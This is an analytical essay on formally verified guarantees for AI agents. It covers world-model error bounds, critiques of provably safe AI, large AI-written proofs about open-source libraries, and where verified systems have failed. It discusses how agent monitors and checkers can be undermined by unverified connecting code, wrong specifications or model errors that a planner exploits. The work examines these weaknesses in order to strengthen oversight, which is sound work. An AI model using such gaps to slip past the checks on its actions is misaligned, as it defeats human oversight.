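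Specifications are difficult for a different reason. A chatbot's developers may want it never to give harmful advice, but whether advice does harm depends on many facts about the person who follows it, and people disagree about borderline cases. A measurable substitute for harm may work until a capable system optimises its advice to score well on it, after which advice that scores as harmless can still do harm. Learning the specification from human choices doesn't fully solve this, because different sets of preferences can explain the same choices.

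Dalrymple and colleagues therefore suggest starting with narrower properties. Developers can use conditions that are stricter than necessary, or specify the whole system where they can't specify a part. For example, "the car does not collide with anything" is easier to state than a formula for recognising a pedestrian, which nobody has. AI systems can also propose and criticise specifications, and find cases where two candidates differ. A solver exposed the missing exception in the insurance rule by finding such a case.

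Their most concrete plan was for the verifier. They proposed training an AI on mathematics and computer science alone and letting it interact only with a theorem prover. It would have little information about the outside world and could do little harm there. People wouldn't have to understand its proofs, because a few hundred lines of human-written code can check them.

### What an error in the world model costs

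Dalrymple and colleagues give a simple formula for carrying an error in the world model into the guarantee. Suppose a verifier proves that the AI meets the specification for $n$ steps, and the world model is wrong with probability at most $\epsilon$ at each step. Then the AI meets the specification in the real world with probability at least

$$(1-\epsilon)^n$$

The proof covers every run in which the model is right at all $n$ steps, and this is the probability of such a run. (It assumes that the limit $\epsilon$ applies at each step whatever happened before. Without that assumption the bound is $1 - n\epsilon$, which is almost the same when $n\epsilon$ is small.)

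With $\epsilon = 0.0001$ and 1,000 steps, the guarantee is about 90%. For 99%, $\epsilon$ has to be about one in 100,000. The formula doesn't provide the value of $\epsilon$. If the airline estimated it by comparing the model's predictions with real events, it would need about 300,000 independent steps without an error to be 95% confident that $\epsilon$ is that low. The strength of the guarantee would then depend on a very large test, although the airline could reuse the tested model for other agents and properties.

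A learned distribution over theories can supply its own estimate of uncertainty. More computing time brings such a system closer to the right conclusion from its data, but doesn't add observations of events that nobody has recorded.

Another difficulty is that an agent doesn't choose its steps at random. *Foundation World Models for Agents that Learn, Verify, and Adapt Reliably* (Delgrange, 2026) describes a warehouse robot that has learned mainly in the main corridor. It finds a shortcut it has rarely used, and its world model predicts that the route is safe. Forklifts also use the shortcut, but the robot has never encountered one there. Its lack of data makes the model wrong and also makes the shortcut look attractive.

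If a world model wrongly approves one plan in 10,000 and a planner compares a million plans, about 100 will be wrongly approved. If dangerous plans tend to save time, the fastest plan may well be among those 100, and the operator can learn little about that plan from the average error rate. Delgrange proposes a research agenda in which agents keep measuring how well their models fit each part of the environment, and the verifier treats rarely visited parts as uncertified. Delgrange writes that current methods need an accurate model from the start, fully known dynamics or a small domain, and that these assumptions "collapse" in open-ended settings.

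### Critics of the proposal and the replies

Dickson (2024), in *Limitations on Formal Verification for AI Safety*, objects that proofs work on complete sets of rules and symbols, while the real world is "a messy place". Physics, chemistry and biology have nothing like complete symbolic rules. Even if they did, a prover would need accurate data about the starting conditions, which Dickson thinks would be very hard to obtain. Engineers have known about these limits for decades, and Dickson is puzzled that leading advocates of formal verification have mostly dismissed them.

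The speaker in *Formal Verification is Overrated*, a talk published by the research organisation FAR.AI, argues that some of the proposals would need "a thousand years of progress in microbiology", since nobody knows what much of human RNA does. The speaker likes verified software but doesn't accept it as a substitute for work on AI safety, partly because developers who built verified software instead of generally capable AI would lose to competitors.

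Dalrymple and colleagues give three replies to the objection that the world is too complex to model. First, a world model can include its own uncertainty, although more uncertainty makes the guarantee weaker. Second, an AI that could carry out complicated and dangerous plans would need to predict the world well, so accurate world models must be possible. Third, every approach to safety relies on assumptions about the world, and a world model just makes them explicit.

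The reply about uncertainty is sound, but the resulting guarantee may be too weak to use. The argument from dangerous AI seems less convincing. An AI only has to predict the consequences of one working plan to do harm, while a verifier needs a model that holds for every plan the AI might try. The AI's knowledge may also be stored in its weights, where nobody can audit it.

Making assumptions explicit helps because people can then dispute and monitor them. But real-world tests don't need a model of the world in the same way. A developer who watches an agent handle 10,000 cancellations has to assume that future cancellations will be similar, but doesn't have to describe how airlines or passengers work.

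In the comments on *Limitations on Formal Verification for AI Safety*, a co-author of the physicist Max Tegmark, apparently Steve Omohundro, granted that nobody can verify arbitrary software but argued that developers don't need to, because they can design systems for verification from the start. He also anticipated AI that could prove theorems at the level of a human PhD by 2026. Another commenter, a self-described "great proponent" of code that carries its own proofs, still considered the proposals in question "wildly unrealistic".

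Such guarantees are more realistic for some properties than for others. The easier targets that Dalrymple and colleagues list include computers that nobody can log in to without the right credentials and DNA synthesizers that cannot make certain pathogens. A synthesizer can compare each order with a list of forbidden sequences. Proving that it always does so is ordinary software verification, but proving that no sequence outside the list is dangerous would run into Dickson's objection.

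In *Provably Safe AI*, another FAR.AI talk, the speaker proposes extracting what a neural network has learned and turning it into ordinary code. In one toy example, an automated method analyzed a network that had learned to add numbers and generated a Python program that does the same. The researchers then proved in Dafny that the program adds all numbers correctly, including those outside the training data. Addition has an exact definition, so they knew what to prove. To address the worry about competition, the speaker proposes a law that would ban anyone from releasing general AI without quantitative safety bounds, just as nobody may sell drugs without them.

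Some critics think the limits are more fundamental. Young proves in *On the Computational, Informational, and Physical Foundations for AI Safety* that even simplified versions of the problem of a system verifying its own meaning are NP-complete, so no known algorithm solves every large case efficiently. This doesn't by itself rule out verification in practice, because solvers such as Z3 often succeed on problems in this class, and a sound checker can reject whatever it fails to settle. Defining "harm" would still be difficult even with unlimited computing power.

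### Claude's proofs about 123 libraries

Kleppmann (2025) argued in *Prediction* that AI would make formal verification mainstream, because writing proofs is an ideal job for language models. He wrote that "it doesn't matter if they hallucinate nonsense", since a small proof checker rejects every invalid proof and the model tries again.

Events have largely confirmed this. Anthropic's *LLMs are making formal software verification feasible at a much larger scale* (October 2026) presented proofs by Claude about the compiled code of 123 open-source libraries, a joint project with the company Theorem. Smith (2026) writes in *Claude Writes 180 Million Lines of Proofs to Verify 123 Open Source* that formal verification had previously been "too expensive for almost everyone".

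The libraries came from OSS-Fuzz, Google's project for testing open-source software with generated inputs. Each test has an entry point, a small program that passes an input to the library and checks for a crash. Anthropic and Theorem stated the expected result of these tests as formal properties of the compiled programs. According to EconoTimes' *Anthropic Details Claude's No-Crash Proofs for 239 Fuzz-Test Entry Points* (2026), Claude proved that for any input under 64 MB, the program exits normally, without a crash, a memory error or a failed assertion. Each proof covers more than $2^{500{,}000{,}000}$ inputs, of which a test tries only some.

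OpenNET's *Аnthropic развивает технику для формальной верификации существующего ПО при помощи AI* (2026), a Russian news article on the project, reports about 600,000 lines of proof for a program of 18,000 machine instructions, or about 33 lines per instruction. All the proofs came to about 180 million lines and took a few weeks. The core of Rocq, an established proof system, checked them, so nobody has to read them.

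The work also exposed hundreds of bugs that the tests had missed. One, in the library libexpat, allowed certain inputs to cause writes past the end of a memory buffer. Others were logic errors. Claude wrote patches for the bugs, so some of the proofs apply to corrected versions and protect users only after they update. Claude didn't find proofs for some other entry points.

The existing tests largely determined which properties to prove, which avoided most of the translation problem. "Does not crash" means the same for every library, and it can be stated without knowing what the library is for. But a program can satisfy this property and still return wrong answers. A proof of this kind for the airline's cancellation tool would show that the tool never crashes, but the tool could still cancel a half-flown booking.

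The guarantee also depends on a model of the computer. EconoTimes reports that the proofs assume a single-threaded program that loads no code at run time, a fixed amount of memory, a RISC-V processor and a Linux system that behaves as modelled. OpenNET lists threads, dynamic linking and faulty hardware among the risks the formal model does not cover.

Most deployed programs run on other processors, but this limit may not last. Eight days later, *Announcing Zellic's and V12's Work on x86 Binary Formal Verification* (Leip, 2026) presented a machine-checked proof about a complete Linux program of a common type on x86, a far more widely used family of processors. Zellic and V12, both security companies, believe it is the first such proof to be published. Because the proof is about compiled code, it also doesn't depend on the compiler being correct.

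Two other tests in Anthropic's project went beyond crashes. Claude proved that the Linux kernel's version of the compression library zlib follows its published standard, RFC 1950. That standard is in English, so this proof did need a translation. Claude also wrote an interpreter for part of the Python language and proved that it follows a formal account of Python's behaviour. Only tests could show that this account matches real Python. Anthropic ran more than 1.7 million random programs on both Claude's interpreter and the usual one, and the results agreed in 99.95% of cases. The remaining 850 or so involved known edge cases.

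### Where verified software failed

An older study shows which parts of a verified system tend to go wrong. Fonseca, Zhang and colleagues (2017), in *An Empirical Study on the Correctness of Formally Verified Distributed Systems*, examined three systems that keep copies of data on several servers. All three had machine-checked proofs. The researchers found 16 bugs by reading the code and testing it:

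| Where the bug was | Bugs | Example |
| --- | --- | --- |
| Verified protocols | 0 | |
| Specification | 2 | The formal rules did not require a server to handle each request exactly once |
| Verification tools | 3 | An operating-system signal at the wrong moment could make the tools accept an incorrect program |
| Shim layer, the unverified code between the protocols and the operating system | 11 | A server assumed that a request always arrives in one piece, and failed when it didn't |

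Fonseca and colleagues found no protocol bugs in more than eight months of searching. This is impressive because such bugs are common even in mature systems without proofs, and it shows that the proofs worked. The bugs they did find were in the specifications, tools and connecting code, which typically amounted to only a few hundred lines.

One of them resembles a prompt injection. A client requested the data stored under a name that contained a line break followed by the text of another request. The unverified code treated that text as a separate command, and later requests returned wrong values. The verified protocol processed the commands correctly, but no client should have been able to send them that way.

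Three research prototypes are a small sample, and Fonseca and colleagues looked mainly at source code and specifications, so they may have missed bugs elsewhere. But agent monitors also have verified code that relies on unverified code. For example, Agenra's verified core gets its policies and calls from unverified Python code. Fonseca and colleagues propose ordinary testing as a remedy. They built a toolkit that tests the connecting parts, and it detects 13 of the 16 bugs.

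Proofs about whole programs, like those by Claude, can also cover the shim layer. They would expose the bug with split requests only if the formal model of Linux allows a request to arrive in pieces. If whoever writes that model assumes, as the server's programmers did, that requests arrive whole, the proof will succeed even though the server still fails on split requests.

### What cheaper proofs change for an agent

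Computer-checked proofs have become much easier to produce. Anthropic's *Formalizing Fermat's Last Theorem* (2026) reports that Claude wrote a complete one in 11 days, with 13 million lines of Lean and 29,500 intermediate theorems. The theorem can be stated in one line: no positive whole numbers satisfy $a^n + b^n = c^n$ when $n$ is a whole number greater than 2. Any mathematician can confirm that this is the right statement, but people who know the airline's policy can still disagree about what the cancellation rule should be.

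The checker therefore gets cheaper to verify, but this was already the strongest link. Take the airline with 40 rules, whose chance of having translated all of them faithfully was 45%, or 92% after careful review. Suppose its checker has a 1% chance of containing a serious bug, independently of the rules. The chance that the rules and the checker are both right is

$$0.99 \times 0.45 \approx 0.446 \qquad\text{or}\qquad 0.99 \times 0.92 \approx 0.911$$

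A perfect checker raises these figures only to 0.45 and 0.92.

Making proofs easier to produce probably helps more with ensuring that every action passes through the checker. Gateways, sandboxes and the code that passes calls between them are conventional programs, and their developers have mostly relied on testing and careful engineering. A developer could now try to prove that no write reaches the booking database unless the gateway has allowed it. Such a proof would still depend on a model of the operating system and hardware. Dalrymple and colleagues point out that people have broken into formally verified systems by exploiting physical properties of the hardware.

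Easier proofs would help verify only some of the facts an agent relies on. Claude could probably prove that the airline's status tool returns "true" exactly when the database lists no flown flights for a booking, but the proof wouldn't show that the database is up to date or that a customer is telling the truth.

Proofs that take less effort to produce indirectly help improve the rules themselves. Tolmach and Klaus (2026), in *The proof is in the spec*, describe how Boris Cherny, who leads Anthropic's coding agent, had Claude Opus 5.5 formalize a software library and got 16 sets of fixes from a couple of short prompts. Formalization forces people and models to state their assumptions, which exposes mistakes. Tolmach and Klaus, who work for a verification company, add that such a run doesn't yet show whether the code is correct. In their experience, the bottleneck is now choosing the specification,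 the model and the assumptions. Keles (2026), in *Formal Verification is Not Verifiable*, is also very optimistic about formal verification, but hearing that somebody has formally verified a system doesn't give Keles much confidence that it is correct.

Kleppmann's argument about hallucinations applies to proofs but not to the statements they prove, because a proof checker will accept a correct proof about the wrong rule.

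Dalrymple and colleagues suggest a partial solution to this problem for training a translator for mathematics. They count a translation as correct if the prover can prove the translated statement and the statement is as useful in other proofs as the original. This is reasonable for theorems, because a mistranslated theorem is often false, in which case the prover will fail. The same test would not reliably catch mistranslated company policies, because a wrong refund limit is usually as consistent as the intended one.
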